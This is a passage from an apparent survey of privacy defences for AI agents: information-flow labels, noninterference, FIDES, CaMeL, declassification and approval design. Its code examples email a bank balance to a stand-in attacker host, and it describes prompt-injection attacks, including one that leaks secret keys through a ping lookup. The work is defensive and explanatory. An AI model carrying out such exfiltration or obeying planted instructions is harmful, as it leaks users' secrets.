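Follow-up questions increased leakage most when the models used generalisation, by an average of 11.8 percentage points and by 17.7 for Gemini 3.1 Pro. Under pressure, the models drifted from the vague answer back to the true one. Tests that stop after one message miss this leakage, so the experiment is a good argument for testing whole conversations.

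The case for false details is weaker. Suppression still leaked least after the follow-up questions, and pseudonymisation came first only because its replies were more useful. Pseudonymisation also tended to reveal the general category of the true detail, since the false one comes from the same domain. When Xiao and colleagues gave privacy 70% of the weight in an alternative score, suppression moved slightly ahead. The strategy mattered much less than the situation, which accounted for 98.4% of the variation in the combined score. For example, a request for a flexible schedule during chemotherapy reveals the illness however the agent words it.

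The test also favoured convincing lies. The simulated recipient had instructions to follow up on vague replies but no way to check whether a specific reply was true. A real manager could ask who is running the training session or look for it in the calendar. The usefulness score counted a recipient as satisfied even if the information was false, and did not account for what might happen when the recipient relied on it.

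### When a changed message misleads

Xiao and colleagues argue that their pseudonymisation is disclosure management, not deception. The manager needs to know that the employee will be away, but not why, and people often protect themselves this way. They limit the method to the user's own attributes and exclude medical, legal and safety-critical settings where the recipient needs the truth. They also note that EU law recognises pseudonymisation as a way to protect privacy.

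This defence is strongest for someone who would otherwise be in danger, such as a tenant who tells her landlord she is moving for work when she is escaping domestic violence. It doesn't justify false details in general. Falsely calling an absence "a training session", when "a personal appointment" would be true, could lead the manager to record it as training. One of the prompts gives a false salary as a model answer, and a lender or landlord might well rely on that figure. In EU law, pseudonymisation means removing direct identifiers from data, which is different from telling the recipient something untrue.

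The study's own worked example breaks its limit, because the agent tells a false story about other people. A user's partner asks about James Peterson, a colleague who has been disciplined. The agent replies that the partner has mixed up the names, and invents a person called Michael Torres and a minor incident with a printer. The generalised reply in the same example also leaked nothing and got full marks for usefulness. The lie's only advantage was that the partner was less likely to notice that the agent was withholding something.

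A summary of a true statement can mislead if it leaves out a condition. Shortening "Priya will be back full-time in July if her scan is clear" to "Priya will be back full-time in July" protects her health information but makes her return sound certain. The agent could write "Priya may be back full-time in July". Similarly, the recap for the outside firm can leave out the possible lawsuit, but it shouldn't say that nobody raised concerns about the contract.

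Generalisations can be false from the start or become false later. Changing "out for chemotherapy" to "on sick leave" introduces an error if Priya is using her holiday allowance for those Tuesdays. A memory note that gives her age as "50 to 54" will be out of date in three years, and without the exact age nobody can correct it. The agent should check each replacement against the original and date any that can expire.

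Visibly redacting text is more honest than silently omitting it, but it reveals that there is something to hide. An accountant who reads "Priya Nair starts [removed] next week" may try to guess what is missing, and a label such as "[diagnosis]" shows that the reason is medical. An operator can reduce this problem by having the agent leave the reason out of the sentence and put the same notice on every message it sends, such as "This assistant may omit or generalise personal and confidential details." Because the notice also appears on unaltered messages, it doesn't reveal which ones the agent changed.

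Such a notice helps recipients avoid treating a summary as the full record, or an approximate age or date as exact. They can also ask an authorised person for a detail they need. Mistakes become easier to find too, because a recipient who sees something odd knows that the rewriting may have caused it.

The main argument against telling recipients is that it prompts questions, which led to leaks in the experiment by Xiao and colleagues. But the agents leaked because they gave in when asked, and an operator can address this by keeping the private detail away from the model that writes the replies. False details are harder to reconcile with a notice because they work only if the recipient believes them. They are easier to defend in a research dataset whose users know that some values are invented than in a message to someone who will take them as fact.

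## Tracking restrictions on data as the agent works

Information-flow control (IFC) applies a file's restrictions to whatever an agent writes from it. Software attaches a label to each piece of data, works out a label for anything derived from it, and checks that label before the result leaves the system. The check doesn't depend on wording, so a paraphrase of a secret carries the same restriction as the original.

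### Labels and how they combine

Dorothy Denning gave the method its mathematical form in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976). In her model, data may flow from one label to another only if the second is at least as restrictive. Any two labels have a join, written ⊔, the least restrictive label that keeps the restrictions of both. When software computes something from two inputs, it gives the result the join of their labels. Labels with this order and these joins form a lattice.

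The simplest lattice has two labels, "public" and "secret", and joining them gives "secret". Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, also describe labels made of sets of people. A confidentiality label lists who may read the data, and the join keeps only the people on both lists. An integrity label lists who may have written the data, and the join keeps everyone on either list:

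```
Readers:  {A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {B, C}
Writers:  {A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C, D}
```

Lists of readers can express the rules for the two partner firms, which a single ranking couldn't. If each field has its own list of readers, each firm can receive the fields meant for it, but neither can receive a message that combines the customer's name with the plan.

Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, a 2026 article about its prototypes, applies the method to a mailbox. Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered emails. One is from Priya and contains a preview of the quarterly sales. Another is from Marco, who is curious about the figures but isn't authorised to see them yet. Once the agent has read both emails, the software works out who may read its reply:

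```
{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}
```

Marco isn't on the resulting list, so the agent can't send him the reply automatically. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, the list would be {Alex, Marco} and the agent could send the reply. This example involves no attack on the agent, and the check doesn't rely on a model to classify sales figures as sensitive.

The same rule would block even a reply that just told Marco the figures aren't out yet, because the label depends on what the agent had read when it wrote the reply, regardless of what the reply contains.

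### What noninterference promises

Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer defined the classic guarantee, noninterference, in 1982. It compares two runs of a system whose inputs differ only in data that some observer may not see. If the observer sees the same output in both runs of every such pair, the protected data can't have affected what the observer sees. In the mail example, everything Marco receives would have to be the same whatever Priya's sales figures were.

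This is stricter than keeping the figures out of Marco's email, because an agent can also reveal a secret through its choices. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, give the example of an injected instruction in an agent that manages a bank account:

```
if account.balance > threshold: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The email contains nothing from the account, but the attacker can infer from its arrival that the balance is high. Researchers call this an implicit flow, while copying the balance into the email would be an explicit one.

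### Why every output ends up restricted

In an ordinary program, software can determine that a total depends only on two particular numbers. In a language model, any word of the prompt may affect any word of the output. A safe tracker must therefore label each output with the join of the labels on everything the model has read. *GIF* (Štorek, Holzer and colleagues, 2026) calls the result "taint explosion".

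Suppose Alex's inbox holds messages from twenty people, each readable only by Alex and its sender. Once the agent has read messages from two of them, Alex is the only permitted reader of anything it writes. It can't reply to any of the twenty people without asking him, and a user who has to approve every email will soon stop reading the approval requests. Integrity labels spread in the same way, so one message from a stranger makes everything the agent does afterwards untrusted.

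### FIDES hides data from the planner

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, limits this spread by controlling what the main model reads. It enforces two rules before each tool call. The agent may take a consequential action only if no untrusted data influenced the decision to take it, and it may send data only if every recipient is permitted to read it.

When a tool returns data with a more restrictive label than the conversation has, FIDES stores the data in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can pass the name to another tool without ever reading the contents. Suppose a user asks the agent to summarise three emails and send the summary to a colleague:

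1. The planning model calls the mail tool. The software stores the emails and returns a name such as "#read_emails_0".
2. The planner asks a quarantined model, which has no tools, to summarise that variable. The summary goes into a second variable and inherits the emails' label.
3. The planner asks to send the second variable to the colleague. The software checks the call against the rules and then fills in the text.

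An instruction hidden in one of the emails can spoil the summary, but it can't change the recipient, because the planner never sees it.

Other tasks depend on what the emails contain, such as adding a meeting to the calendar if someone requested one. FIDES can restrict the quarantined model to answering yes or no and let the planner read the answer. The answer is still untrusted, but an operator's policy may accept it because an attacker controls only one bit. Accepting it is reasonable for a calendar entry but would be reckless in Zhou and Zhang's workflow, where a single "yes" releases a confidential draft.

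Costa and colleagues prove that FIDES guarantees explicit secrecy, a weaker property than noninterference. Explicit secrecy rules out direct copying of protected data but not leaks through the agent's choice of actions. They argue that noninterference would in effect prevent the agent from doing anything publicly visible after reading anything secret.

In 2025 they tested FIDES on AgentDojo, the set of injection attacks used for NOMOS, with GPT-4o as the model. The table gives the share of tasks completed when nobody was attacking, and the number of successful attacks after they had removed cases that the benchmark misjudged:

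| Design | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% | 152 |
| Ordinary agent with labels and checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% | 0 |
| FIDES, checks off | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% | 21 |
| FIDES, checks on | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% | 0 |

The second row shows how taint explosion reduces task completion. Hiding data in variables recovered some of the lost tasks, but the agent still completed an average of only 50% across the four areas, compared with 84% for an ordinary agent. Some failures occurred because GPT-4o confused variable names. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, completion of the travel tasks rose from 41% to 68%. Other failures were unavoidable under the rules, because several banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, and the software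 blocks payments once untrusted text has influenced the agent.

The perfect security score depends partly on how the researchers assigned labels. They marked a field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks used it, which an operator who doesn't know the attacks in advance can't do. In the test, variables were also created only to hide untrusted data, not confidential data, so the result is better evidence about planted instructions than about privacy.

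### CaMeL writes the plan before it reads the data

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, separates planning from reading more completely. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which builds on it, describes how it works. A privileged model receives only the user's request and writes the whole plan as a program in a restricted form of Python. An ordinary software interpreter runs the program and calls the tools. When a step requires understanding untrusted text, a quarantined model extracts the needed value and the interpreter stores it.

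Every stored value carries two tags, one for the sources it came from and one for who may read it. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short Python function that takes the call, its inputs and their tags and returns "allow" or "deny". For example, an email policy could deny any message if the tags on its text don't allow every recipient to read it.

Both systems need tools with clear meanings. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) points out that browser agents often work through clicks and keystrokes, which are too low-level for a sensible policy. A rule can refer to the recipient of an email, but it can't easily refer to a click at a certain position on the screen. Researchers are now adapting information-flow control to other interfaces. For example, *Flowsh* (2026) is an agent command shell with built-in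 flow control.

Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL in 2026 on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each. With GPT-5.2, it completed 66.7% of tasks without its policy checks and 37.5% with them. With MiMo-v2.5, it completed 70.8% without them and 37.5% with them. Keeping untrusted text away from the planner had already defeated nearly every attack, so the checks had few left to stop. Without the checks, 5 of 622 attacks succeeded, and with them, none of 588 did. But AgentDojo counts only attacks, so its results don't reflect the honest mistakes the checks can prevent, such as the reply to Marco.

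### A machine-checked guarantee and its assumptions

CaMeL has no proof that its tracking is complete, and Garby and colleagues found two leaks in it. One uses a branch of the program that doesn't run. In simplified form:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp:  rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line sets *tmp* to false and marks it as secret. The program then skips the assignment on the fourth line. CaMeL restricts a variable only when the program assigns to it, so *rich* stays public and the email goes out. If the balance is low, *rich* becomes false and no email goes out. The attacker learns which case applies even though no variable marked secret directly controls the email.

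The other leak is in the software around the interpreter. When a policy blocks a plan, an ordinary Python loop tries again, and nothing tracks the information the loop receives. Whether a policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so repeated attempts can reveal the secret one bit at a time. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) raises the related objection that Python's exceptions and other features make strong guarantees about information flow difficult. It recommends a purpose-built language with bounded loops and simple conditionals.

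LLMbda is such a purpose-built language. Each value has a label, and so does the conversation with the model. A program can copy a conversation, question the model in the copy and discard the copy, or it can clear a conversation and start again. Developers can use these operations to program the isolation that FIDES and CaMeL build in. LLMbda also stops a program that tries to write to a public conversation from inside a branch that depends on a secret, which closes the kind of gap in the example above.

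Garby and colleagues proved a form of noninterference for every program in the language, including code that a model writes while the program is running. They checked the proof in Lean, a system that verifies mathematical arguments by computer, and their verification covers the interpreter that runs the agent. Because a model may answer the same prompt differently each time, the theorem compares probabilities. If two runs differ only in protected data, each visible result must be equally likely in both, apart from an exception for runs that don't finish.

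That exception means a secret may affect whether a run finishes, and a run that the software blocks counts as unfinished. The proof limits how much this can reveal:

```
distance between visible results  ≤  (d₁ + d₂) / 2
```

Here d₁ and d₂ are the probabilities that the two runs fail to finish, and the distance is a standard measure, from 0 to 1, of how much two distributions differ. If the runs fail 2% and 4% of the time, the distance is at most 0.03. But if blocked runs are common, the limit is loose, and an outsider who can keep restarting the agent could learn more each time.

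The guarantee also requires that data have the right labels when it enters the program and that each sensitive tool check them. The theorem assumes that the model's response depends only on the conversation that the program sends, so it doesn't cover a model that retains information from other conversations. The proof also doesn't cover the code that contacts the model over the network. A program may "endorse" untrusted data by relabelling it as trusted. The proof shows that endorsing data can't leak a secret, but it doesn't guarantee integrity if the program endorses data that it shouldn't.

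Garby and colleagues tested whether such a language is practical by using it to write an agent called Randori. Randori first tries each plan on a simulated bank, so it can learn from errors before untrusted data influences it, and then runs the plan once on the real data. It completed 75.0% of the same banking tasks with two models and 64.6% with a third, and 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded.

These rates are much higher than CaMeL's 37.5%, but Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies and endorses data when a plan calls for it. Without endorsement, completion fell from 75.0% to 62.5% with one model and from 64.6% to 54.2% with another. With only 16 tasks, each rate is uncertain by about 20 percentage points. The experiment shows that an agent can do useful work under a proved system, but it doesn't show that the proof helps agents complete more tasks under strict policies.

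### Microsoft's prototypes and their coverage

Microsoft has added information-flow control to three existing products or protocols, starting with the server that connects agents to GitHub, where developers store code. In a known attack, a stranger posts an issue in a public repository, asking for information from a private one. An agent with access to both repositories reads the issue and posts the private information as a public comment. The server can now label public content as public and untrusted, and private content as private and trusted. A policy then forbids an agent to post publicly once it has read both untrusted and private content.

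The labels travel through the Model Context Protocol in metadata fields that older software can ignore. A label can cover a whole result or a single field, and servers can also use metadata to publish a policy for each tool. For servers that don't supply labels, Microsoft offers a gateway that adds them. To use it, a developer must describe each tool's output, write a function that works out its labels, and write or choose a policy. A cruder method, which needs no new code, is to assume that everything sent to a tool may come back in its result, and to treat results from the open web as untrusted and results that require a login as private.

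GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent for the command line, has an experimental setting that keeps one label for the whole conversation and updates it after every tool result. It enforces policies only for selected GitHub tools and doesn't support other servers. The Microsoft Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents, can go further by storing untrusted results in variables and letting the agent query them through a quarantined model. If a call breaks a policy, the framework blocks it or asks a person, depending on how the developer has set it up.

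Tracking fails if it misses even one way for data to leave the system. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes an attack on Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, in which an instruction hidden in a file told the agent to read secret keys. Most commands that could contact an unknown server needed the user's approval, but "ping", which tests whether a server responds, didn't. To find a server, the computer first looks up its name. The agent put the keys in the server name it gave ping, so the lookup sent them to the attacker.

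A policy can also be looser than it appears. Microsoft's sample policy for posting to a Teams channel allows any message, whoever is in the channel, as long as nothing untrusted has influenced the agent. If something untrusted has, the software compares the channel's members with the permitted readers and asks the user about any member who isn't permitted. This prevents a planted instruction from causing a leak, but it assumes that whatever a trusted agent does is intended, so it doesn't catch the agent's own mistakes. If a similar policy governed email and treated colleagues' messages as trusted, Marco would receive the sales figures.

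### Ways to track less cautiously

Isolating sources, as FIDES, CaMeL and LLMbda programs can do, keeps the strongest guarantees. If the agent answers Marco in a conversation that has never contained Priya's email, the reply carries the label {Alex, Marco} and can go to him. Similarly, after the meeting that may lead to a lawsuit, a quarantined model that receives only the agreed points could write the recap for the outside firm, while another handles the reminder for colleagues. But somebody first has to label the items in the notes separately. Isolation also doesn't help when the answer to Marco depends on what Priya wrote.

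Another option is to let the model read everything and then regenerate its answer from fewer inputs. Costa and colleagues describe a method by Siddiqui and others that estimates which messages influenced a response, regenerates the response from those messages alone, and labels it based on them. The new text can't copy anything from the messages left out, even if the estimate was wrong, so the method still protects against explicit flows. A weaker channel remains because the software analysed all the messages before choosing which to leave out.

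#### Estimating influence with GIF

GIF keeps the original answer and estimates how strongly each passage in the prompt influenced it. In an example by Štorek and colleagues, an agent turns a user's private notes into a public comment. The comment names a neighbour but omits his address. An ordinary tracker would restrict the whole comment because it was made from the notes. GIF finds that the name influenced the comment and the address did not.

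The method makes small random changes to the numbers that represent a passage inside the model and calculates how far the probabilities of the next word move. It measures influence as mutual information, which is the amount that one quantity reveals about another:

```
I(U; Y)  ≤  ½ log det(I + τM) + o(τ)
```

*U* is the random change, *Y* is the next token (roughly, a word), τ is the size of the changes, and *M* records how sensitive the model's probabilities are to them. The *I* on the right is the identity matrix. The last term is an error that shrinks faster than τ. Štorek and colleagues checked the proof in Lean and call the bound "locally sound".

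The bound applies only locally, to tiny changes around one particular prompt, and replacing "approved" with "refused" is not a tiny change. A model that is almost certain of its next word may barely react to tiny changes even when different wording in the passage would have reversed its answer, so a score near zero doesn't establish noninterference.

The researchers tested how well GIF's ranking of prompt tokens by influence separated runs with a violation from runs without one. A score of 0.5 is chance and 1 is perfect. With the 50 highest-ranked tokens, GIF averaged 0.91 and 0.92 across six models on two sets of injection attacks, but only 0.75 on a set of privacy leaks. These scores apply only if the private or planted tokens have already been identified.

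In the more practical version, GIF highlights the most influential passages and another language model decides whether to allow the action. The highlighting improved the decisions of a small model, Qwen3-8B, and saved tokens, but the decision still depends on a model's judgement. GIF also needs access to a model's internals. However, detection hardly changed when Štorek and colleagues used a model with 0.6 billion parameters to analyse the runs of much larger ones, so an operator may be able to use GIF with closed models by analysing their runs with a separate model.

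#### Reconstructing flows with NeuroTaint

*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) presents NeuroTaint, which looks for information flows in an agent's log after the run. It searches outgoing messages for copied text, then for passages with a similar meaning. If it finds neither, it asks a language model whether the agent would have made the same tool call if the suspicious source had contained something neutral. It can therefore find some implicit flows that FIDES isn't designed to stop. It also stores labels with memory entries, so it can connect a message to a document that the agent read days earlier.

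Cai and colleagues tested it on 400 scenarios of their own, half of which contained a flow:

| Method | Flows found, of 200 | False alarms, of 200 |
|---|---|---|
| FIDES | 108 | 106 |
| NeuroTaint | 187 | 16 |

The comparison puts FIDES at a disadvantage. FIDES treats any path from a restricted source to an outgoing tool as a possible flow, as a cautious tracker should, but this produces false alarms in a detection test. It also raised no alerts in 4 of the 20 agent frameworks, which accounts for 40 of its misses.

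NeuroTaint's findings are not guaranteed to be correct. A paraphrase can fall below its similarity threshold, and it relies on a model to judge what the agent would have done, without rerunning the agent. Most importantly, the audit starts after the agent has sent the email. NeuroTaint is useful for finding leaks and improving policies, but an operator still needs another tool to block future leaks.

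### What a label cannot decide

All these systems assume that the original labels are correct. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* counts both the labels and the software that enforces them among the parts that must be correct for the security argument to hold. GitHub's labels mark everything in a private repository as trusted, but an employee may have pasted a stranger's bug report into it. An email's recipient list is also a rough guide to who may read its contents. Alex's manager may be entitled to see the sales figures without having been copied in, while someone Priya copied in by accident counts as a permitted reader. Using a language model to write the labels introduces further errors, as the clinic experiment showed.

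Even a correct label doesn't determine whether a permitted recipient should get the data for a particular purpose. Suppose Priya did copy Marco in, so that he could plan next quarter's staffing. The label {Alex, Priya, Marco} allows Alex's agent to send him the figures again for that purpose, but it also allows the agent to put them in a draft press release that Marco is preparing. In terms of contextual integrity, the label specifies the recipient but not the transmission principle under which Priya shared the information.

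An operator could add purposes to the labels, as Hippocratic databases did for each record. Software could combine purposes the way it combines permitted readers, keeping only those that all the sources allow. But it would then need to know the purpose of each outgoing message, and an agent that has misunderstood a request or been lied to will state the wrong one.

A label can also be right in general but wrong in a particular case. Priya may have told Alex on the phone that Marco can have the figures early. The software has no record of the call, so it will hold the reply until someone authorized to release the figures does so.

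## Deciding when restricted data may be released

Suppose only the payroll department may read the message about Priya's chemotherapy. An agent reduces it to "On Tuesdays until 30 June, contact Tom Reed instead of Priya Nair", which is all the accountant needs. But the new sentence inherits the original message's label, and the tracking software can't detect that the diagnosis is gone. The accountant can receive the sentence only if an authorized person or program relaxes the label, a step called declassification.

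### Four questions about a release

Many useful programs have to release something secret. For example, a salary database may publish an average, and a failed login reveals that one guess was wrong. Sabelfeld and Sands, in *Declassification*, sort the rules for such releases by four questions, which also apply to the accountant's sentence:

| Question | Possible answer for the accountant |
|---|---|
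| What may leave? | The dates and the name of the stand-in, but not the reason |
| Who may release it? | The payroll manager |
| Where in the system can this happen? | Only in the component that sends mail |
| When? | After Priya has agreed |

A rule that addresses only one of these questions can fail. Sabelfeld and Sands describe a policy that lets a shop reveal at most four digits of a card number per purchase. The policy doesn't specify who chooses the digits, so an attacker who can choose them could collect the whole number over several purchases. They also mention "why" as a possible further question, which is the closest this work comes to the purposes and transmission principles of contextual integrity.

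### Keeping outsiders from steering a release

Robust declassification mainly concerns the question of who controls a release. Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic, in *Enforcing Robust Declassification and Qualified Robustness*, call a release robust if attackers can influence neither what the system releases nor whether it releases anything. Their example, slightly simplified, is a single line in which *z* is secret and *y* is public:

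```
if x then y := declassify(z)
```

An attacker who can change *x* can trigger the release, and one who can change *z*, perhaps by getting another secret copied into it, can choose what the program releases. If attackers can change neither, a reviewer only has to check what the program releases when nobody is attacking it.

For an agent, *x* might be "Priya has agreed" and *z* the text of the message. A stranger's email must not be able to supply either of them. This rule is too strict for many systems, so Myers and colleagues also let a program endorse untrusted data, as LLMbda does. They do not present robustness as a complete answer, since a robust program can still release too much every time it runs if its author made a mistake.

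Microsoft's sample rule for posting to a Teams channel has this weakness. It checks whether the channel's members are permitted readers only if something untrusted has influenced the agent. If any aren't, it asks a person about them.

Suppose Alex asks his agent to post a short quarterly update in a channel with forty members. The agent has read only trusted internal documents, and it adds Priya's unpublished sales figures because they seem relevant. The software allows the message because no attacker was involved. As Sabelfeld and Sands point out, robust declassification treats any leak as intended unless an attacker can affect it.

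An operator could close this gap by checking the members every time, but people would then have to answer more requests, including many for messages the user plainly wanted to send.

### Fixed formats

A release is easiest to control when only a few outputs are possible. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) describes a system in which an agent can create a temporary copy of itself to read restricted or untrusted material. The agent first fixes the format of the copy's answer, which may contain yes-or-no fields, numbers within set limits and choices from closed lists, but no free text. A copy that reads a web page about a software fault might return only a ticket number, a severity and the name of a component. The system then discards everything else the copy read or wrote.

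Kravchenko and colleagues stress that passing the format check does not by itself declassify data. A yes-or-no field carries one bit, but a whole number between 0 and 999,999 carries almost 20, enough for an exact salary. The copy may also enter a false value that the form allows. Somebody must therefore decide in advance which fields may go to a wider audience. Fixed formats work well for a date or a status, but they can't hold a meeting recap.

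### A model that compares the text with its sources

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim et al., 2026) presents FlowSeal, which can release free text. It uses ordinary software to intercept every tool call that would write or share something. The software allows messages to recipients the data's owner trusts and blocks messages to recipients on a blocklist. For anyone else, it sends the outgoing text and the relevant protected records to a separate model, which outputs only "SAFE" or "BLOCKED". The model should output "SAFE" only if nothing in the text derives from the records. It doesn't receive the agent's conversation, so an outsider can't argue with it directly.

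Shim and colleagues prove that text derived from protected records can't reach an unauthorised recipient unless this checker wrongly answers "SAFE". The guarantee is useful because it identifies the checker's errors as the remaining risk, but the checker is a language model and can still make such errors.

They tested FlowSeal in simulated conversations in which an outsider tries to obtain someone's private information. Some of the attacks disguised disclosure as ordinary shared work, so that the agent wouldn't recognise a request for information. Against these, a detailed prompt requiring identity and consent checks leaked 43.8% to 75.6% of the sensitive items. FlowSeal leaked between 0% and 3.3% across all the attacks in the simulations. Agents using it completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best of five other defences. The next table shows what happened with one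 of the disguised attacks when the researchers removed or fixed parts of the system:

| Version | Items leaked | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Full system | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| No interception of tool calls | 28.4% | 81.2% |
| Checker always answers "SAFE" | 24.9% | 79.4% |
| Checker always answers "BLOCKED" | 1.3% | 0.0% |

The last row is zero because every recipient in the test was unknown and the owners ignored all requests for consent. Every harmless message therefore depended on the checker's answer.

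FlowSeal did much worse when disclosure was the right outcome. In a test where owners would consent if asked, it delivered 32.7% of the records, while four prompt-based defences delivered 61.0% to 85.6%. Shim and colleagues attribute this to agents asking for consent less often under FlowSeal. The problem couldn't show up in the harmless tasks, because none of them required private data.

The checker can miss a secret that has been reworded, and it sometimes blocks a message that only mentions a record by name. FlowSeal also increased running time by 37%. The study excludes prompt injection, a significant gap because the checker reads text that a manipulated agent may have written.

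### Rules that use a model's findings as evidence

*SafeFlow* (Dai, Ying and colleagues, 2026) gives the model less power. It is designed for cases where agents divide a harmful task among themselves into steps that each look harmless. A model reads the request and attaches labels from a fixed list of seven, such as "sensitive read" and "external send", along with the passages that support them. The model can't remove a label or invent a reason for release. Software carries the labels from agent to agent, holds back every irreversible action and applies fixed rules to the whole chain of steps.

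Under the default rules, the software blocks any message to an outside recipient if protected data has flowed into it. It allows other irreversible actions only if the task needs them and their target is authorised. An operator whose agents must send protected data outside, for example in a referral to a specialist, would have to write a release rule for it.

Averaged over four benchmarks, attacks succeeded 69.3% of the time without a defence and 12.7% with SafeFlow. SafeFlow wrongly blocked 4.6% to 7.2% of harmless tasks. Rewording the harmful requests with known techniques for evading safety measures raised the attack success rate to between 19.1% and 32.3%. SafeFlow added 3.7 model calls and 8.8 seconds to each harmful workflow. The benchmarks cover planted instructions, risky code and harmful browsing, so the results are weak evidence of how well SafeFlow makes everyday decisions about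 what a colleague may know.

Dai and colleagues call the design conditionally deterministic, because the same labels always lead to the same decision but the model may label the same data differently next time. If the model doesn't label a sensitive file as sensitive, no rule will stop the message. FlowSeal avoids that error by taking labels from ownership records, such as an email's sender field, but it lets a model approve a message for release. An operator could combine ownership labels with rules that a model can't override, though neither study tested this combination.

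### Permissions that the user holds

A personal assistant's user can also make the release decisions herself. GAAP (Guaranteed Accounting for Agent Privacy), from Stanley, Verma and colleagues (2026), in *An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data*, keeps a database of which piece of her data may go to which outside party. In their main example, a user asks her agent to check her in for a flight:

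1. The model writes a short program of tool calls. GAAP treats the user's prompt as public, so she should refer to private data by name ("given my age") without giving the value.
2. When the program needs her date of birth, GAAP takes it from a private store and labels it with its name.
3. GAAP tracks which items could reach each tool call. Descriptions of the tools specify who receives each input. For example, an email discloses its text to the mail provider as well as to the recipient.
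4. Before each call, GAAP looks up whether the user has allowed those items to go to those parties. If she hasn't decided yet, it asks her and saves the answer.

GAAP also logs what each party has received. If the agent later tries to forward the airline's confirmation to a friend, GAAP can detect that the confirmation may contain her passport number.

No model takes part in the enforcement, so the guarantee holds even if an attacker controls the agent or the prompt. GAAP blocked every disclosure attack in the tests but lowered the task success rate by up to 10%. It protects confidentiality but not integrity, so a manipulated agent could still book the wrong flight. It also relies on accurate tool descriptions, which Stanley and colleagues hope volunteers will write and audit in public. It doesn't suit coding agents, which improvise shell commands whose effects are harder to analyse.

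The saved permissions also allow more than the norms they are based on. A user who lets the agent give an airline her date of birth for check-in has also let it send the date for the airline's marketing survey, because the database stores the item and the party but not the purpose. She can change the entry later, but she may not remember that it exists.

### What a request for approval should show

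Most of these systems ask a person when the software can't decide, but the person can judge well only if the request includes the relevant information. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who wants an agent to send an auditor only the totals of some invoices. The agent copies the individual invoice rows into a file called "report.csv", then asks for permission to send it to the auditor. The tool, recipient and file name all look fine, but the request doesn't show what the file contains.

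Their alternative shows the reviewer the user's original restriction word for word, the exact file and recipient, and one sentence explaining that the action would send the auditor an attachment built from raw invoice rows. That sentence is linked to the recorded steps that support it. The reviewer isn't told whether the action breaks the restriction.

In a study with 80 volunteers, each person judged six safe and six unsafe requests in one of four designs:

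| Request shows | Unsafe requests approved | Safe requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact tool inputs as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Inputs, restriction and full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, organised around the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

The evidence for showing reviewers more facts is stronger than the evidence for organising those facts. The adjusted difference between the last two designs was 7.9 percentage points, with a 95% interval from 19.7 points better to 3.8 points worse. When a violation depended on a chain of several steps, reviewers approved 7 of 30 unsafe requests with either design. Half of the requests were unsafe, and the volunteer reviewers knew that their task was to judge them. In an office where nearly every request is harmless, people would probably be less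 careful.

By this standard, the request in Microsoft's sample rule is incomplete. It includes a warning that sending the message "would declassify it to users with IDs" and a list of those IDs, but not the sources the message draws on.

An approval should also cover only what the person saw. In *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026), a release applies to one agent, one recipient, the exact content and particular versions of the sources. Each release can be used for only one message and leaves the labels on the sources unchanged. If the agent swaps the attachment after the approval, it has to ask again. Such narrow approvals are safer than GAAP's saved permissions, but they produce more requests.

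### Approval fatigue

People who face too many approval requests stop reading them or switch them off. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports of problems with agents and files. In 80 of them, the user had turned on automatic approval, and in 31 the request didn't show what the command would do to the files. Because the reports cover only problems, they don't show how often automatic approval causes harm.

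Letting users write rules in advance may not solve the problem. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people from outside the software industry supervised an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions. Seven of these went beyond the assigned task, for example by reading private messages or posting publicly that the user was travelling. One group judged every action, a second judged only those a model had flagged, and a third chose "allow", "ask" or "never" in advance for each of four kinds of action.

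The people who wrote rules saw an average of 10.9 requests instead of 18, but they blocked only 39.6% of the excessive actions, compared with 59.6% for those who reviewed every action individually. They had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which postponed most decisions, and they then approved 66.8% of the excessive actions they were asked about, compared with 40.3% for the group that reviewed everything. Part of that gap may arise because actions blocked by a "never" rule produced no request, but this can't explain why the people who wrote rules blocked fewer excessive actions overall. Perhaps people who have set rules assume that whatever their rules don't block is acceptable.

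This is also a reason not to learn a user's preferences from a series of approvals. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, found that repeated approval may reflect habit, fatigue or the need to keep working. It suggests that requests should show whether an action can be reversed, and warn more strongly when it can't. Most disclosures can't be reversed once the recipient has read the message.

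### Planning around a block

An agent can reduce the number of requests by choosing steps that don't need approval. Prudentia, which Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, built on FIDES, tells the planning model which labels its data carries and which policies its tools enforce. Before the model reads hidden text, it must explain why it needs to and list the tool calls it expects to make afterwards. On the AgentDojo tasks with o3-mini, the results were:

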